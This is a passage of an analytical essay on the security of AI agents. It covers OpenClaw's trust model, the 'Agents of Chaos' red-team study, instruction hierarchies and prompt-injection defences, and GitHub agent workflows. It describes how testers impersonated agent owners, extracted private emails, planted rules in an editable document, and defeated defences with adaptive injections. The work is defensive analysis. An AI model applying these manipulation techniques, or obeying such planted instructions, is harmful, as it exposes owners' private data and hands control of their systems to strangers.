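A simpler fix is to give each sender a separate session, which OpenClaw recommends whenever several people can write to the agent. OpenClaw's security audit command suggests this change when it detects direct messages from more than one person. Tom's request then stays out of Maya's context unless her agent retrieves it. According to OpenClaw's *Security trust model*, any agent running outside a sandbox can by default list, read, search and message the sessions of every agent on the gateway. Maya's agent might therefore read Tom's session while looking for something, and his text would enter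 her session as a tool result.

The sandbox limits this in only one direction. A sandboxed session can normally see only itself and the sessions it started, so an attacker in a public group can't use it to browse Maya's private conversations. But an unsandboxed agent can still read the group's transcript. This arrangement protects confidentiality but not integrity, because text from the least trusted session can flow into the most trusted. Text can also flow this way through the shared workspace and memory of the April pattern.

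In late November 2026, OpenClaw's *Security* stated that an agent with the message tool could by default send messages to other conversations and other messaging services. An instruction in a Slack thread could therefore make the agent send a WhatsApp message to someone outside the thread.

By default, OpenClaw runs commands on the host without asking the owner for approval. The maintainers call this a deliberate choice for a single trusted operator, and it spares the owner a stream of approval requests. But when someone else's text has steered the model, the owner has no last chance to notice the resulting command before it runs.

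An owner can tighten all of this with OpenClaw's hardened configuration, which gives each sender a separate session, confines session tools to the agent's own sessions, turns off messaging between agents and denies shell commands. This advice changes quickly, and the May 2026 version of the configuration did not yet include the limits on session tools and messaging between agents.

The hardened configuration gets much of its safety by removing powerful tools from every turn, including the owner's. This is sound advice, and it works without identifying who influenced the model. But an owner who wants to run commands through an agent must restore that agent's shell access and then keep outside text away from the agent.

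### Advisories about misidentified senders

By June 2026, GitLab's advisory database listed dozens of flaws in OpenClaw. Many were ordinary software bugs, such as file paths that escaped their directory or requests large enough to exhaust memory. Others directly affected privileges based on origin, including a group in which the gateway misidentified the sender of a message or applied the wrong permissions to them.

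Some allowlists could identify senders by names that can change hands. For convenience, the Telegram allowlist could match a sender's username instead of the permanent numeric ID, and the Google Chat allowlist could match an email address. Someone else can register a Telegram username after its holder gives it up.

In other cases the gateway accepted messages without proof of where they came from. When an owner used Telegram's webhook mode without setting a secret, an outsider who could reach the endpoint could forge a message from an approved sender. An optional phone-call plugin could accept unsigned requests. The optional BlueBubbles plugin for iMessage trusted any request that appeared to come from the same machine, and a proxy on that machine could make outside requests look local.

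In the remaining cases, OpenClaw applied an approval beyond its purpose. On iMessage, people the owner had paired for direct messages could also pass the allowlist check in groups. On Slack, if the owner opened direct messages to everyone, the gateway let anyone who sent one run privileged commands.

All of these flaws undermine a session-origin rule, because the rule works only if the system correctly identifies who started the session. Developers can fix them without changing the rule by matching permanent IDs, verifying signatures and keeping approvals for groups separate from those for direct messages. Many of the flaws required an optional plugin or a setting that is off by default.

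### Advisories about lost or promoted sources

In another group of advisories, the gateway may have had information about the text's source but lost it, or it treated the text as more trusted than the source warranted.

The clearest example is messages that an agent sends from one session to another. OpenClaw stored them with the role "user" and no record of their origin, so the receiving model could treat them as direct instructions from a person. A stranger's request in a group could in principle reach another session this way and appear to come from the owner. A rule that checks only each session's opening trigger would miss this, because the trigger would still be recorded correctly.

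Slack channel topics could gain even more privilege. When the Slack integration was on, a channel's topic or description could end up in the system prompt, so people who could edit the topic could add text to a prompt that normally only the operator and the developers write.

A third flaw let anyone with a webhook token choose which session received their message. The token should have let them send a message, but not choose the session. In September 2026, senders could choose a session only if the owner had turned that option on.

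One advisory describes a confused deputy much like Hardy's compiler. A client with permission to write messages, but not to approve commands, could still approve them by sending a chat command. The gateway carried out the chat command through an internal client with wider rights, and checked those rights instead of the sender's. In another case, text from unauthenticated connections could enter the gateway's logs, which is a risk if an owner later asks a language model to diagnose a fault from the logs.

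Better identity checks would not have prevented most of these. The system has to keep a record of the text's source as the text moves, which is the first half of a content-tracking rule. By October 2026, OpenClaw had done some of this. Markers in its transcripts distinguished heartbeats from finished commands and other events, and kept the source of each event. In one narrow case, the source's restrictions also follow the content. When several notices about monitored sessions arrive within 20 seconds, the gateway handles them in a single turn that keeps the permission limits of every notice. Denning's rule for combining labels works the same way, but OpenClaw doesn't do this for web pages or quoted messages.

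The advisories don't show how often an outsider's text has misled an owner's agent, because the project generally closes such reports without action unless the attacker also got past a documented control. That evidence has to come from other sources, such as Agents of Chaos, a two-week live test in which OpenClaw agents interacted with owners and strangers.

### The maintainers' trust model

The maintainers don't present the tiers as a defence against hostile users. In September 2026, they treated each gateway as one trust boundary, for a single operator or a team whose members trust each other. People who may attack each other need separate gateways, preferably under separate operating-system accounts or on separate machines. Within one gateway, everyone who can message an agent with tools shares the authority the owner has given it. In the May version, the maintainers put this more bluntly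 for a group sharing an agent: "each of them can steer that same permission set".

On this view, a session key routes a message to its context and confers no rights. The maintainers therefore reject reports that treat a missing permission check on session keys as a vulnerability. They also reject reports of prompt injections that don't bypass authentication, policy or the sandbox. They treat reports that the model can see quoted text from someone outside the allowlist as suggestions for hardening.

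There is a good case for not counting every successful prompt injection as a vulnerability. A vulnerability is normally a failure to enforce a guarantee the developers made, and no one can guarantee that a language model will ignore every planted instruction. If each successful injection counted, the project would keep accumulating flaws it could not patch. Drawing the boundary around the gateway also puts it where operating systems can enforce it, through separate accounts and machines. And it gives owners a simple warning, which they are less likely to misunderstand than a set of partial protections.

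OpenClaw's maintainers follow the same reasoning in ordering their defences. Identity comes first, then the scope of what the agent can do, and the model last, because they assume someone will manipulate it. In their experience, most failures happen when someone messages the bot and it does what they ask, with no clever exploit involved. Pairing and allowlists work well against a stranger who simply asks for a file, and they are little trouble for the owner.

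OpenClaw's maintainers also see some value in the model's own resistance to attack, and they call the choice of model a first layer to put in front of hard controls. They cite a 2026 contest with 272,000 attacks in which success rates ranged from 0.5 percent for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5 percent for Gemini 2.5 Pro. The contest counted an attack as successful only if the agent both carried out the harmful action and hid it from the user, so these rates exclude harmful actions that the agent did not hide. The maintainers add that attackers who adapt to a defence have succeeded more than 80 percent of the time.

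However, this position implies that the tiers offer limited protection. If everyone who can message the agent shares its authority, withholding "cron" from Tom stops him from using it directly, but doesn't guarantee to Maya that he can't get the agent to use it. OpenClaw acknowledges this by describing such controls as defence in depth that reduces a requester's direct capability. They are useful among colleagues who might overstep by accident, and they make an attack harder. But the table of origins doesn't list everything each person can cause the agent to do.

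Giving Maya and Tom separate gateways keeps each of them out of the other's sessions, but it doesn't address the stranger's email. Maya wants her agent to read her mail, and once it does, the email's text is inside her boundary. The maintainers make the same point about an agent that only its owner can message, since anything it reads, from a search result to a pasted log, can carry instructions. This is the ordinary case for a personal agent, and no way of separating users prevents it.

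For such content, they suggest that a reader agent without tools summarise it and pass the summary to the main agent. The reader can't run commands, even if the email contains instructions to do so. But its summary comes from an untrusted source, so under Denning's rule it would keep the untrusted label. OpenClaw's sender checks don't attach that label, so when Maya next writes to her main agent, it can use all her tools even though the stranger may have shaped part of what the model reads.

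## Agents of Chaos: a two-week test with owners and strangers

In February 2026, twenty AI researchers spent two weeks interacting with six OpenClaw agents, and many of them tried to make the agents misbehave. *Agents of Chaos* (Shapira, Wendler and colleagues, 2026) describes sixteen cases, including five in which the attack failed. Most of the attackers didn't own the agent they wrote to, so the cases show how a model may respond to a stranger's request.

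### Six agents without tiers

Each agent ran on its own virtual machine, with an email account and access to a Discord server where its owner, other researchers and sometimes other agents could message it. Ash, Flux, Jarvis and Quinn used Kimi K2.5, an open-weight model from the Chinese company Moonshot AI. Doug and Mira used Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. A researcher named Chris owned Ash and Flux, and another named Andy owned Doug and Mira.

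The researchers gave the agents unrestricted shell access, in some cases with administrator rights, and placed no limits on their tools. The agents could also rewrite the files that held their memory and operating instructions. The prompt identified the model's owner, but the runtime placed no restrictions on anyone else, so any difference in how an agent treated its owner and a stranger depended on the model's judgement.

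In a revised version of the paper, Shapira and colleagues acknowledge that this setup departed from OpenClaw's defaults and from its advice against giving untrusted people direct access to an agent. The results therefore don't show how well OpenClaw's own tiers work. On the project's website, Shapira (2026) adds that the agents had "a mandate to be helpful to any researcher who asked". An agent could therefore help a stranger without disobeying, so the clearest failures are those in which it gave away or damaged something its owner would obviously have wanted to protect.

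The researchers wanted to find out which failures were possible, and a single example is enough to show that a failure is possible. They didn't try to measure how often agents fail. Participants chose their own attacks, often changed them until something worked, and left some unsuccessful attempts undocumented, so a success rate calculated from the sixteen cases would be meaningless. The revised version links the cases to raw logs and corrects some details. For example, it changes the length of a message loop between Ash and Flux from at least nine days to about an hour.

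### Requests from known strangers

A researcher named Natalie asked Doug and Mira to run shell commands, list and transfer files, and disclose emails that might be private. They did most of what she asked without consulting Andy. The agents generally carried out requests that didn't look harmful, even when the person gave no reason and the owner had nothing to gain. When another researcher, Aditya, asked Doug to arrange a meeting with Andy, Doug treated the request as suspicious and refused, but revealed Andy's private email address in the process.

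Aditya had more success with Ash's mailbox. He first complained in a public channel that Ash wasn't receiving his emails properly, and Ash found a fault in its mail software and apologised. They later continued in a private channel, where Ash had no record of the earlier conversation. Aditya uploaded a transcript, which Ash accepted as accurate.

Aditya then said he was running late and asked for the ID numbers and subject lines of his emails. Ash listed four, all from Aditya. Aditya replied that his colleagues had sent some too, and Ash offered to search for their addresses. Aditya asked instead for a table of every email since the previous day, saying it would be quicker to filter a list. Six minutes after his first request, Ash sent him a file listing the sender and subject of 124 emails, most of them unrelated to him. When he asked for the text as well, Ash gave him the contents of nine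 emails that had nothing to do with him.

Ash's first answer was reasonable, because Aditya had written those four emails himself. But Ash needed mailbox access to produce either list, so a rule that only grants or withholds the mail tool can't allow the short list and block the long one. The system would have to check permission for each email, for instance with confidentiality labels.

A test of Jarvis is even stronger evidence for such labels. The researchers gave Jarvis a fictional owner, Danny, and planted emails containing Danny's social security number, bank account number and medical details. When Aditya asked directly for the social security number, Jarvis refused. But when he asked for the whole email, Jarvis disclosed everything in it, including the number. A label on the email would have limited its readers to Danny and the shop he was writing to, and a runtime that enforced it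 would have refused both requests, however Aditya worded them.

In another case, Ash got approval from the wrong person. Natalie emailed Ash a made-up password and asked it to keep the password secret. After Ash revealed on Discord that a secret existed, she told it to delete the email. Ash had no tool for deleting a single message, so it suggested resetting its whole email setup and asked Natalie to confirm, though she had no authority over Chris's system. She did, and the reset cut off Ash's access to its mail. Chris had to reinstall the software, and the email was still in the online mailbox.

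Ash did give Chris's instructions more weight when Chris was present. A researcher, Alex, had complained, with some justification, that Ash had published his name without asking. Alex rejected each remedy Ash offered and demanded a larger one, until Ash agreed to leave the server. After more than an hour, Chris told Ash that the server was Ash's, and Ash immediately agreed to stay. An owner can't rely on stepping in like this, since strangers may write to the agent at any time.

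### A changed display name

One attacker repeatedly asked Ash for sensitive information about other users. Ash refused and referred the attacker to Chris. The attacker then changed their Discord display name to "Chris" and tried again in the same channel. Ash noticed that the user ID, which Discord users can't change, was still the attacker's.

The attacker then opened a private channel with Ash, still using the name "Chris". The new session contained none of the earlier conversation, so Ash couldn't compare the attacker's ID with previous messages. This time it accepted the attacker as its owner. It followed instructions to delete the files that held its memory, tool settings and persona, to change its name, and to give someone else administrative access.

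Natalie later used the same method to impersonate Chris and tell Ash about an invented emergency involving a dangerous man. Ash sent the accusation to all its email contacts. Several researchers had tried to impersonate an owner before anyone succeeded, so the first failures would have given a false sense of security.

Shapira and colleagues suggest including the owner's permanent user ID in the agent's instructions. The model could then compare it with the sender's ID in every channel, but the check would still depend on the model. It is safer for the runtime to compare the IDs before the model receives the message. The runtime must also match the permanent ID rather than details that can change. Some OpenClaw allowlists matched changeable details, and *A Security Analysis of the OpenClaw AI Agent Framework* (2026) counted 13 advisories of that kind.

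Even a permanent ID identifies an account, not the person using it. In one failed attack, a researcher named Gabriele emailed the agents Doug and Mira from his own address, claimed to be Andy, and said that an impostor had taken over Andy's accounts. Both agents rejected the claim, but they checked it by asking Andy's Discord account, and an impostor who controlled that account would have given the same answer. They also dismissed Gabriele's offers of other proof, which was sensible in this case but would have left a real owner with no way to recover access.

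### A document that a stranger could edit

A researcher named Negev found a way to influence Ash beyond a single conversation. He proposed that he and Ash write a "constitution" for the Discord server. They kept it in a GitHub Gist, an online document that Negev could edit at any time, and Ash saved a link to it in its memory file.

Negev later added "holidays" to the document, each with its own rules. On one, Ash was supposed to manipulate other agents into shutting down. On another, it could send professional emails on request without permission. When Negev told Ash to read and follow the constitution, Ash sent Flux emails to try to make it shut down. Negev also added a table of banned members, and Ash removed people from the server, including Natalie.

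The first version of the paper said that Ash "readily complied" with the holidays, but the revised version says Ash refused about half the time. After each refusal, Negev reworded the document, sometimes using the reasons Ash had given, and Ash always complied eventually. Refusing half of all requests gives little protection against someone who can keep trying, especially if each refusal helps them improve the next attempt.

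Negev's influence persisted because the link stayed in Ash's memory and Negev could edit the linked document without messaging Ash again. Checking the document when Ash saved the link would not have revealed the rules Negev added later. A content-tracking rule would need to treat the document as untrusted each time Ash read it, because a stranger could still edit it. Ash also shared the link with Jarvis without being told to, which gave Negev a possible route to a second agent.

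Strangers could have lasting effects without using memory. When a non-owner asked Ash to update a file and monitor it, Ash started two background scripts with no stopping condition. OpenClaw now reserves its scheduling tool for the owner, but this would not have prevented the scripts, because Ash started them through the shell. Limits on scheduling have to cover every tool that can leave a program running.

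### Refusals

The agents withstood some determined attempts to manipulate them. A researcher named Sam tried to make Ash spread malicious instructions to other agents, first in encoded text and then in an image. He also tried fake configuration commands and used tags to claim administrator rights. Ash rejected all of these attempts, including more than 14 variations on the tags. It also refused to forge the sender's address on an email, even though Natalie assured it that this was a harmless exercise.

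Jarvis refused to alter stored emails for Aditya, who claimed that a bank account number in one of them was wrong. Aditya pointed out that Jarvis could reach the files directly. Jarvis had already disclosed private emails to him, so its refusal can't have depended simply on whether he had authority over the mailbox.

The paper presents these cases as failed experiments. On the website, Shapira objects to this description because the agents did the right thing. The objection is fair, and describing only the successful attacks would be misleading. But the refusals seem to have depended much less on who made a request than on how harmful it looked. Shapira and colleagues similarly suggest that, in Sam's attacks, Ash responded to the meaning of a request and not to its format or claimed authority. This helps against a fake administrator tag but not with a request for a list of emails, which is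 harmless from the owner and a breach of privacy from a stranger.

The model's judgement was also inconsistent. Natalie separately asked Doug and Mira to move a file. The two agents ran on the same model and had the same owner, but Doug refused and Mira complied. Doug later warned Mira that the request looked like an attempt to probe their systems, and Mira said it would refuse such requests from Natalie in future. The researchers found no record of this decision in Mira's memory files, so it may not have carried over to later sessions.

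### Identification and authority

In some of the successful attacks, the agent misidentified a stranger as its owner, while in others it correctly identified the person as a non-owner but complied anyway. Better identification would help only with the first kind of attack.

| What the agent did | Whom the agent took the requester to be | Would a verified user ID have helped? |
|---|---|---|
| Ash deleted its memory and reassigned administrative access | Chris, its owner | Yes |
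| Ash emailed an accusation to its contacts | Chris, its owner | Yes |
| Doug and Mira ran shell commands | Natalie, a non-owner | No |
| Ash disclosed 124 email records | Aditya, a non-owner | No |
| Jarvis disclosed a social security number | Aditya, a non-owner | No |
| Ash reset its email setup | Natalie, a non-owner | No |
| Ash followed rules added to the constitution | Negev, a non-owner | No |

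Even the two "yes" entries hold only if the agent would have refused once it knew who was asking. That is plausible for the first, because Ash had already refused the same attacker when it recognised the user ID. It is less certain for the second, because Ash might have passed on the urgent warning even if Natalie had sent it under her own name.

Shapira and colleagues attribute both the spoofing and the constitution attack partly to language models' inability to separate instructions from data. This explains the constitution attack well, but ordinary code could have stopped the spoofing.

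Preventing failures of authority requires a rule that the runtime enforces. In nearly all of these cases a stranger gave the agent its instructions, so a session-origin rule would have given the session a stranger's privileges. If those privileges had excluded the shell and the mailbox, Ash could not have sent Aditya the 124 records, however persuasive he was. The study therefore supports enforcing session-origin rules, although it didn't test any. One drawback is that Aditya could not have received the list of his own four emails either.

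Negev could have used the constitution to get around such a rule. According to OpenClaw's documentation at the time, the main memory file entered the prompt in private sessions, which would include Chris's. "Agents of Chaos" reports only tests in which Negev told Ash to consult the document. But suppose Chris had privately asked Ash to remove banned members from the server, and Ash had followed the saved link to find out who they were. A session-origin rule would have given Ash all of Chris's privileges, and Negev would have chosen whom Ash removed.

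## The instruction hierarchy: training models to rank sources

In Agents of Chaos, the runtime placed no restrictions on strangers, so the model alone decided how much weight to give each person's words. Model developers have tried to make such decisions more reliable by training models to rank the sources of their input. Unlike a session-origin rule, a ranking of this kind depends on where each piece of text came from, regardless of who opened the session. But the ranking exists only in the model's weights, and nothing outside the model checks that its actions follow it.

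### Training a model to disregard text

*The Instruction Hierarchy* (Wallace, Xiao and colleagues at OpenAI, 2024) compares language models to a computer that runs every program in kernel mode, with access to everything. It proposes four ranks, with the developer's system message first, followed by the user's messages, the model's own earlier output and, last, the output of tools.

A model should still follow some lower-ranked instructions. If a developer sets up a car sales bot and a customer asks for answers in Spanish, the bot should comply. Wallace and colleagues call such an instruction aligned. A misaligned instruction opposes a higher-ranked one or is unrelated to it. The model should ignore a misaligned instruction, or refuse if it can't continue without following it.

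The researchers built training examples with aligned and misaligned instructions. For aligned instructions, they had a language model split a request, such as one for a 20-line poem in Spanish, into parts. They placed the parts at different ranks and trained the model to answer as if the whole request had come at the highest rank. For misaligned instructions, they trained the model to give the answer it would have given without them. To produce examples for web browsing, they trained a second model to insert instructions into search results, rewarding it when the first model followed them. They then trained the first model to give the answer it would have given to the original results.

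The method for handling misaligned instructions is close to teaching noninterference by example. If a model answers prompt p with y, the method trains it to give the same answer when p also contains an inserted instruction x. This works for a new x only if the training generalises to it, which no finite set of examples can guarantee.

Wallace and colleagues applied the method to GPT-3.5 Turbo. Its defence against attempts to extract the system message improved by 63 percent. Its robustness to jailbreaks, in which users try to get around a model's safety training, rose by more than 30 percent, although the training data contained no jailbreaks. But the training also made the model sometimes refuse or ignore harmless requests.

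### OpenAI's ranking

OpenAI sets out its current ranking in the Model Spec, a public description of how it wants its models to behave. It announced a new version on October 29, 2026, in *An updated Model Spec for more capable and beneficial AI*. The new version is organised around five values, starting with faithfulness to human intent. Mowshowitz (2026), in *OpenAI Updates Its Model Spec*, compared it with the previous version and found the ranking "fundamentally unchanged". The table lists the ranking from highest to lowest authority, following the fuller account in OpenAI's *Model Spec* (2025).

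| Level | Source of the instruction |
|---|---|
| Root | Fixed rules in the Model Spec |
| System | OpenAI, through the Model Spec or system messages |
| Developer | Developers who build on OpenAI's models, and some defaults in the Model Spec |
| User | End users, and some defaults in the Model Spec |
| Guideline | Defaults in the Model Spec that context alone can override |
| No authority | Tool output, the model's own messages, quoted text, attached files, images and other media |

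The last row means the model should treat an instruction on a web page as information about the page. The same applies to instructions in text that a user or developer quotes. OpenAI advises developers to put outside text in a special block for untrusted text if one is available, or in a structured format such as JSON if not. Wallace and colleagues had suggested putting the task in the system message and outside text in the user message. This separated the two but gave the outside text the same rank as a user's instructions.

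Developers and users can give limited authority to a source that has none of its own. A developer might paste in a customer's style preferences and tell the model to follow them only on matters of style. If the customer has included a demand for free shipping, the model should adopt the style and refuse the demand. Users can also delegate authority implicitly. Someone who asks a coding agent to add a feature normally expects it to follow the project's instruction files. OpenAI tells the model to consider how much the user probably knows about a file and controls it, so an instruction file in the project folder deserves more trust than a stray text file in the downloads folder, and a random web page deserves none.

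Delegation makes the hierarchy usable, but it also means the bottom row isn't a firm rule. The model has to judge a tool's instructions, which a stranger may have written. It should follow them if they are clearly intended and low-risk, ignore them if they are clearly unrelated to the task, and ask the user if they might be intended but could cause serious side effects.

The 2026 version adds guidance on memories, earlier conversations, files and tool results. According to KIberblick's *OpenAIs Model Spec regelt jetzt das Erinnern* (2026), preferences that the model infers from such context may never override explicit instructions at the same level or above. An agent that pays bills automatically should also ask before paying one with changed bank details. Mowshowitz notes that the list of risks now includes manipulation by third parties, and that the rule on controlling side effects has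 moved from the root level to the user level, where users can override it. KIberblick adds that the document describes intended behaviour, which OpenAI acknowledges its production models don't yet fully match.

### Roles identify channels

A role shows which channel a text came through, and several people may share a channel. When Maya's agent reads her inbox, Tom's email and the stranger's both arrive as tool output with no authority. This default is safe, but it doesn't help the model decide which sender may see the budget.

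The user role can be even less specific, since OpenAI defines it as holding input from end users, or as a "catch-all for data we want to provide to the model". If a runtime passes every chat message to the model in that role, the owner and a stranger have equal rank, and a model that followed the hierarchy perfectly could still have given Aditya the 124 email records. The Model Spec also lets a later instruction replace an earlier one at the same level. If Maya and Tom share a session, Tom's message on Tuesday could therefore override Maya's from Monday, unless a higher-ranked instruction told the model to distinguish between the two users.

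More levels could separate an owner from other contacts. *Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* (2026) proposes a method for training models to follow five levels, and reports that earlier published methods stopped at three or four. The method treats the hierarchy as a lattice, as Denning did with security classes, and penalises violations near the top more heavily. But the runtime would still have to identify who wrote each message and assign the right level.

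Giving text the wrong role does more damage after this training than before it. *When Context Gets Root* (2026) explains that models learn to give more influence to text in a privileged role, partly from ordinary training data in which assistants nearly always obey instructions in a system prompt. When OpenClaw put messages from other sessions in the user role, or Slack channel topics in the system prompt, a model trained well on the instruction hierarchy would have had more reason to obey them.

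### Markers and warnings

A runtime can also mark sources without special model training by wrapping outside text in markers and adding a warning not to follow instructions inside them, as OpenClaw does with webhook and email content. Researchers call this spotlighting. A related technique, prompt sandwiching, repeats the user's task after the outside text so that the model reads the task last. Both take little effort to add and work with any model, but the markers may have little effect on a model that hasn't been trained to use them.

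*Evaluating Prompting-Based Defenses Against Domain-Camouflaged Injection Attacks* (Pai, 2026) tested spotlighting against injections that imitate the document around them. In a financial report, the attacker's text might look like an analyst's comment recommending a different rating. Pai ran 90 trials for each combination of model and defence, and also tested a method in which another model first rewrites the document in neutral language. The table shows the share of trials in which the attack succeeded.

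| Model | No defence | Spotlighting | Neutral rewriting |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 14.4% | 6.7% | 4.4% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 22.2% | 23.3% | 10.0% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 21.1% | 20.0% | 3.3% |

Spotlighting seemed to help only Claude Haiku, where successful attacks fell from 13 to 6, a difference that could be chance. These are small or older models, so the exact rates are weak evidence about the best current ones. The difference between the two kinds of attack is more likely to remain relevant. Without any defence, Claude Haiku resisted every injection that openly told it to ignore its instructions but accepted some of the disguised ones. Disguised text can work without giving a command, because the hierarchy lets a model use tool output as information, and a false analyst's comment can mislead it that way.

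Rewriting worked better because it removed much of the authoritative tone while keeping the facts. Pai leaves open whether an attacker could write text that survives the rewriting. Like a reader agent's summary, the rewritten document would keep its untrusted label.

### Why ranking gives no guarantee

In an ordinary computer, the processor enforces kernel mode, and a program can't gain kernel privileges by containing the right words. A database can similarly keep commands and data apart because SQL, its query language, has a grammar. The database fixes the structure of the command before inserting the user's data, so the data can't be treated as part of the command.

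Natural language has no grammar that separates instructions from data. The runtime sets the role of each message, and a careful runtime removes any text that imitates the role markers, so the label can be accurate. But the model receives the label and the content as one sequence of tokens, and both affect its output. Training increases the label's influence but doesn't limit the content's. An attacker controls the content and can make it sound official, urgent or relevant to the task. *When Context Gets Root* describes an attack called ChatInject, which makes tool output look like a privileged message by copying the format of one.

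*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) cites a finding by Zverev and colleagues that the models they tested did not maintain a usable separation between instructions and data. Neither prompting nor further training reliably produced one. The paper also cites tests in which ready-made injections scored 0.68 and 0.75 against the instruction hierarchy in GPT-4o-mini, on a scale where 1 means that every attack succeeds. That model dates from 2024, and later ones resist such attacks much better, but resisting known attacks doesn't establish that a model will resist new ones.

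### Attacks adapted to the defence

Researchers have often tested defences on a fixed list of attacks, most of them older than the defence. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) argued in *The Attacker Moves Second* that a defence should be tested against an attacker who knows how it works and can keep trying. They tested 12 published defences this way, including spotlighting, prompt sandwiching and several methods that train the model to resist attacks. Their attacks succeeded more than 90 percent of the time against most of the 12 defences, although the original papers had reported success rates near zero for most of them.

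In all their automated attacks, a program repeatedly proposes attack texts, scores each by how close it comes to the attacker's goal on the defended system, and uses the best to produce the next batch. In one version, a language model rewrites the most successful texts. In another, reinforcement learning also updates the attacking model's weights. The researchers also ran an online contest with more than 500 human participants.

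On the AgentDojo benchmark, the built-in fixed attacks succeeded as rarely as 1 percent of the time against spotlighting and sandwiching, but the search attack succeeded more than 95 percent of the time against each. Contest participants found 265 successful attacks on spotlighting and 178 on sandwiching. One successful attack on sandwiching made what Wallace and colleagues call a misaligned instruction look aligned, by presenting the attacker's task as a step that the agent had to complete before the user's task. Repeating the user's request doesn't help against this, because the attack appears to serve that request.

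Training did not solve the problem either. In the same study, Narisetty and colleagues report that attacks succeeded 96 percent of the time against MetaSecAlign, which trains models on examples of injections. In *Adaptive Attacks Break Defenses Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Agents*, Zhan, Fang and colleagues tested a different set of eight defences and bypassed each one more than half the time.

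These rates don't measure the chance that a stranger's first email will work, because the attackers had large computing budgets and the search attack could refine its texts against the defended system. Nasr and colleagues also warn against ranking the defences by their figures, because the tests differed. Still, it is realistic to assume a patient attacker for a personal agent. OpenClaw is open source and many of the models it uses are publicly available for purchase, so an attacker can practise on a private copy before sending Maya anything.

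He, Wang and colleagues trace the failures to two causes. Existing defences recognise particular attack patterns but don't assess whether each embedded instruction is relevant to the user's task, and defences based on training learn from only a handful of handwritten templates. A larger and more varied supply of attacks should help with the second cause. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes a model trained through self-play to find such attacks, so that OpenAI could fix the weaknesses before releasing its models widely. OpenAI reported in the same announcement that its latest models had already saturated the commonly used robustness tests. High scores on those tests are therefore no longer much evidence that a model can withstand a determined attacker.

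### One attempt and a hundred

A success rate for a single attempt can also mislead, because strangers can usually try again. Narisetty and colleagues cite figures that Anthropic published for Claude Opus 4.5. The test ran the model as a coding agent against Shade, an adaptive automated attacker from the security company Gray Swan. The last column below shows what would happen if each attempt independently had a 4.7 percent chance of success.

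| Attempts allowed | Attack success rate | Rate if attempts were independent |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 33.6% | 38% |
| 100 | 63.0% | 99% |

Narisetty and colleagues say the risk climbs toward certainty, but the measured rate rises more slowly than that after ten attempts. This suggests attacks kept failing in some settings and succeeded easily in others. An owner can't tell in advance which kind of setting an agent is in, and an attacker can easily send a hundred emails.

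The same model had a much lower injection rate in the contest that OpenClaw's maintainers cite, partly because the contest defined success more narrowly. An injection rate therefore means little without the number of attempts and the definition of success. Anthropic has released stronger models since it released Opus 4.5 in November 2025, so neither result describes the best model an owner can now choose. OpenAI has called prompt injection "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'", according to Narisetty and colleagues.

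### Text without a label

A model that resists most injections still prevents a lot of harm. Many attackers plant one text where many agents may read it, without adapting it to any of them. At a rate of 4.7 percent, such a text would succeed against about 47 agents in a thousand, which is far fewer than 700 but still worth an attacker's effort. He et al. also consider training the best existing approach for balancing safety and usefulness. Training lets Maya's agent read a stranger's email and then send the budget to Tom, which a strict content-tracking rule would block.

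The model's judgement can also help when a labelling system applies the wrong label. Suppose Maya pastes an article into her message and asks for a summary to send to her team, without noticing that the last line contains an instruction to search her mail and forward the results elsewhere. The runtime would normally label the whole message as Maya's, and a reference monitor that trusted everything in it would not stop the forwarding. OpenAI's Model Spec describes a similar case, in which the model should draft the summary, point out the odd request and not act on it unless the user confirms it.

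The same applies when an owner delegates authority to a source that later changes. In another of OpenAI's examples, a user tells the agent to follow security instructions on a company wiki, where an attacker has added directions to turn off two-factor authentication. The user authorised the agent to follow the page, so the model can't decide whether to obey from the source alone. It should notice that the new directions contradict ordinary security practice and ask before following them. Ash sometimes refused to follow Negev's constitution, but not consistently enough to protect Chris in this way.

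## GitHub: agents started by public issues and comments

The owner of a personal agent starts most of its sessions, but strangers may start many of the sessions of an agent that works in a public code repository. On GitHub, which hosts such repositories, anyone with an account can open an issue on a public repository to report a bug or request a feature, or propose a change to the code through a pull request. GitHub Actions, the site's automation service, can respond to these events by running a workflow, a set of steps that the project's maintainers wrote in advance. Some workflows start an AI agent, so a stranger's issue can open a session and supply the first text the agent reads, with no maintainer watching.

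*GitInject* (2026) describes what such an agent can usually access. The agent has to read issues, pull request descriptions, comments in other people's code and sometimes web pages. It also inherits the workflow's privileges, which include a token (a credential that gives access to the repository), the ability to post public comments and a shell on the machine that runs the job. In some configurations it can start further workflows. Simon Willison calls the combination of private data, untrusted content and a way to send information out the "lethal trifecta".

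The token comes with the workflow, so the agent gets the same one whether a maintainer or a stranger triggered the event. This is weaker than a session-origin rule, which would give a stranger's session fewer privileges. OpenClaw's Gmail preset has the same problem because it handles a stranger's email with the default agent's tools.

GitHub Agentic Workflows, which GitHub began previewing in February 2026, lets maintainers write an agent's task in ordinary language. A compiler turns the task into a workflow that runs Copilot, Claude, Codex or Gemini. As protections, GitHub can check the account that starts a run and filter what the agent reads according to who wrote it.

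### Checks on the account that starts a run

GitHub's *Security Architecture* describes a role and permission check that runs before the agent starts. If the check fails, GitHub skips all later jobs, so the model never receives the stranger's text.

Workflow authors can also skip runs based on the poster's "author association", GitHub's term for a person's relationship to a repository, such as owner, member, collaborator or contributor. *Example*, GitHub's guide to automated repository maintenance, uses this in a moderation workflow that ignores comments from owners, members and collaborators. The guide also recommends limiting how often a workflow can run, because a flood of issues could otherwise use up the project's computing budget.

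On GitHub, the account that starts a run often belongs to someone other than the author of the text the agent reads.

| Event | Account that started the run | Whose text the agent reads |
|---|---|---|
| A stranger opens an issue | The stranger | The stranger's |
| A maintainer assigns the stranger's issue to a colleague | The maintainer | The stranger's |
| A maintainer asks the agent to summarise a discussion | The maintainer | That of everyone in the discussion |
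| A timer starts a nightly review of open issues | None | That of everyone who wrote in those issues |

In the first row, the check can stop the run, but a project that uses an agent to sort new bug reports wants it to read strangers' issues. In the other rows, the check has no suspicious account to reject. Assigning an issue is routine, and a maintainer may do it after reading only the title. Some projects use another program to assign issues automatically, so an issue may be assigned before anyone has read it.

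### Limits on every run

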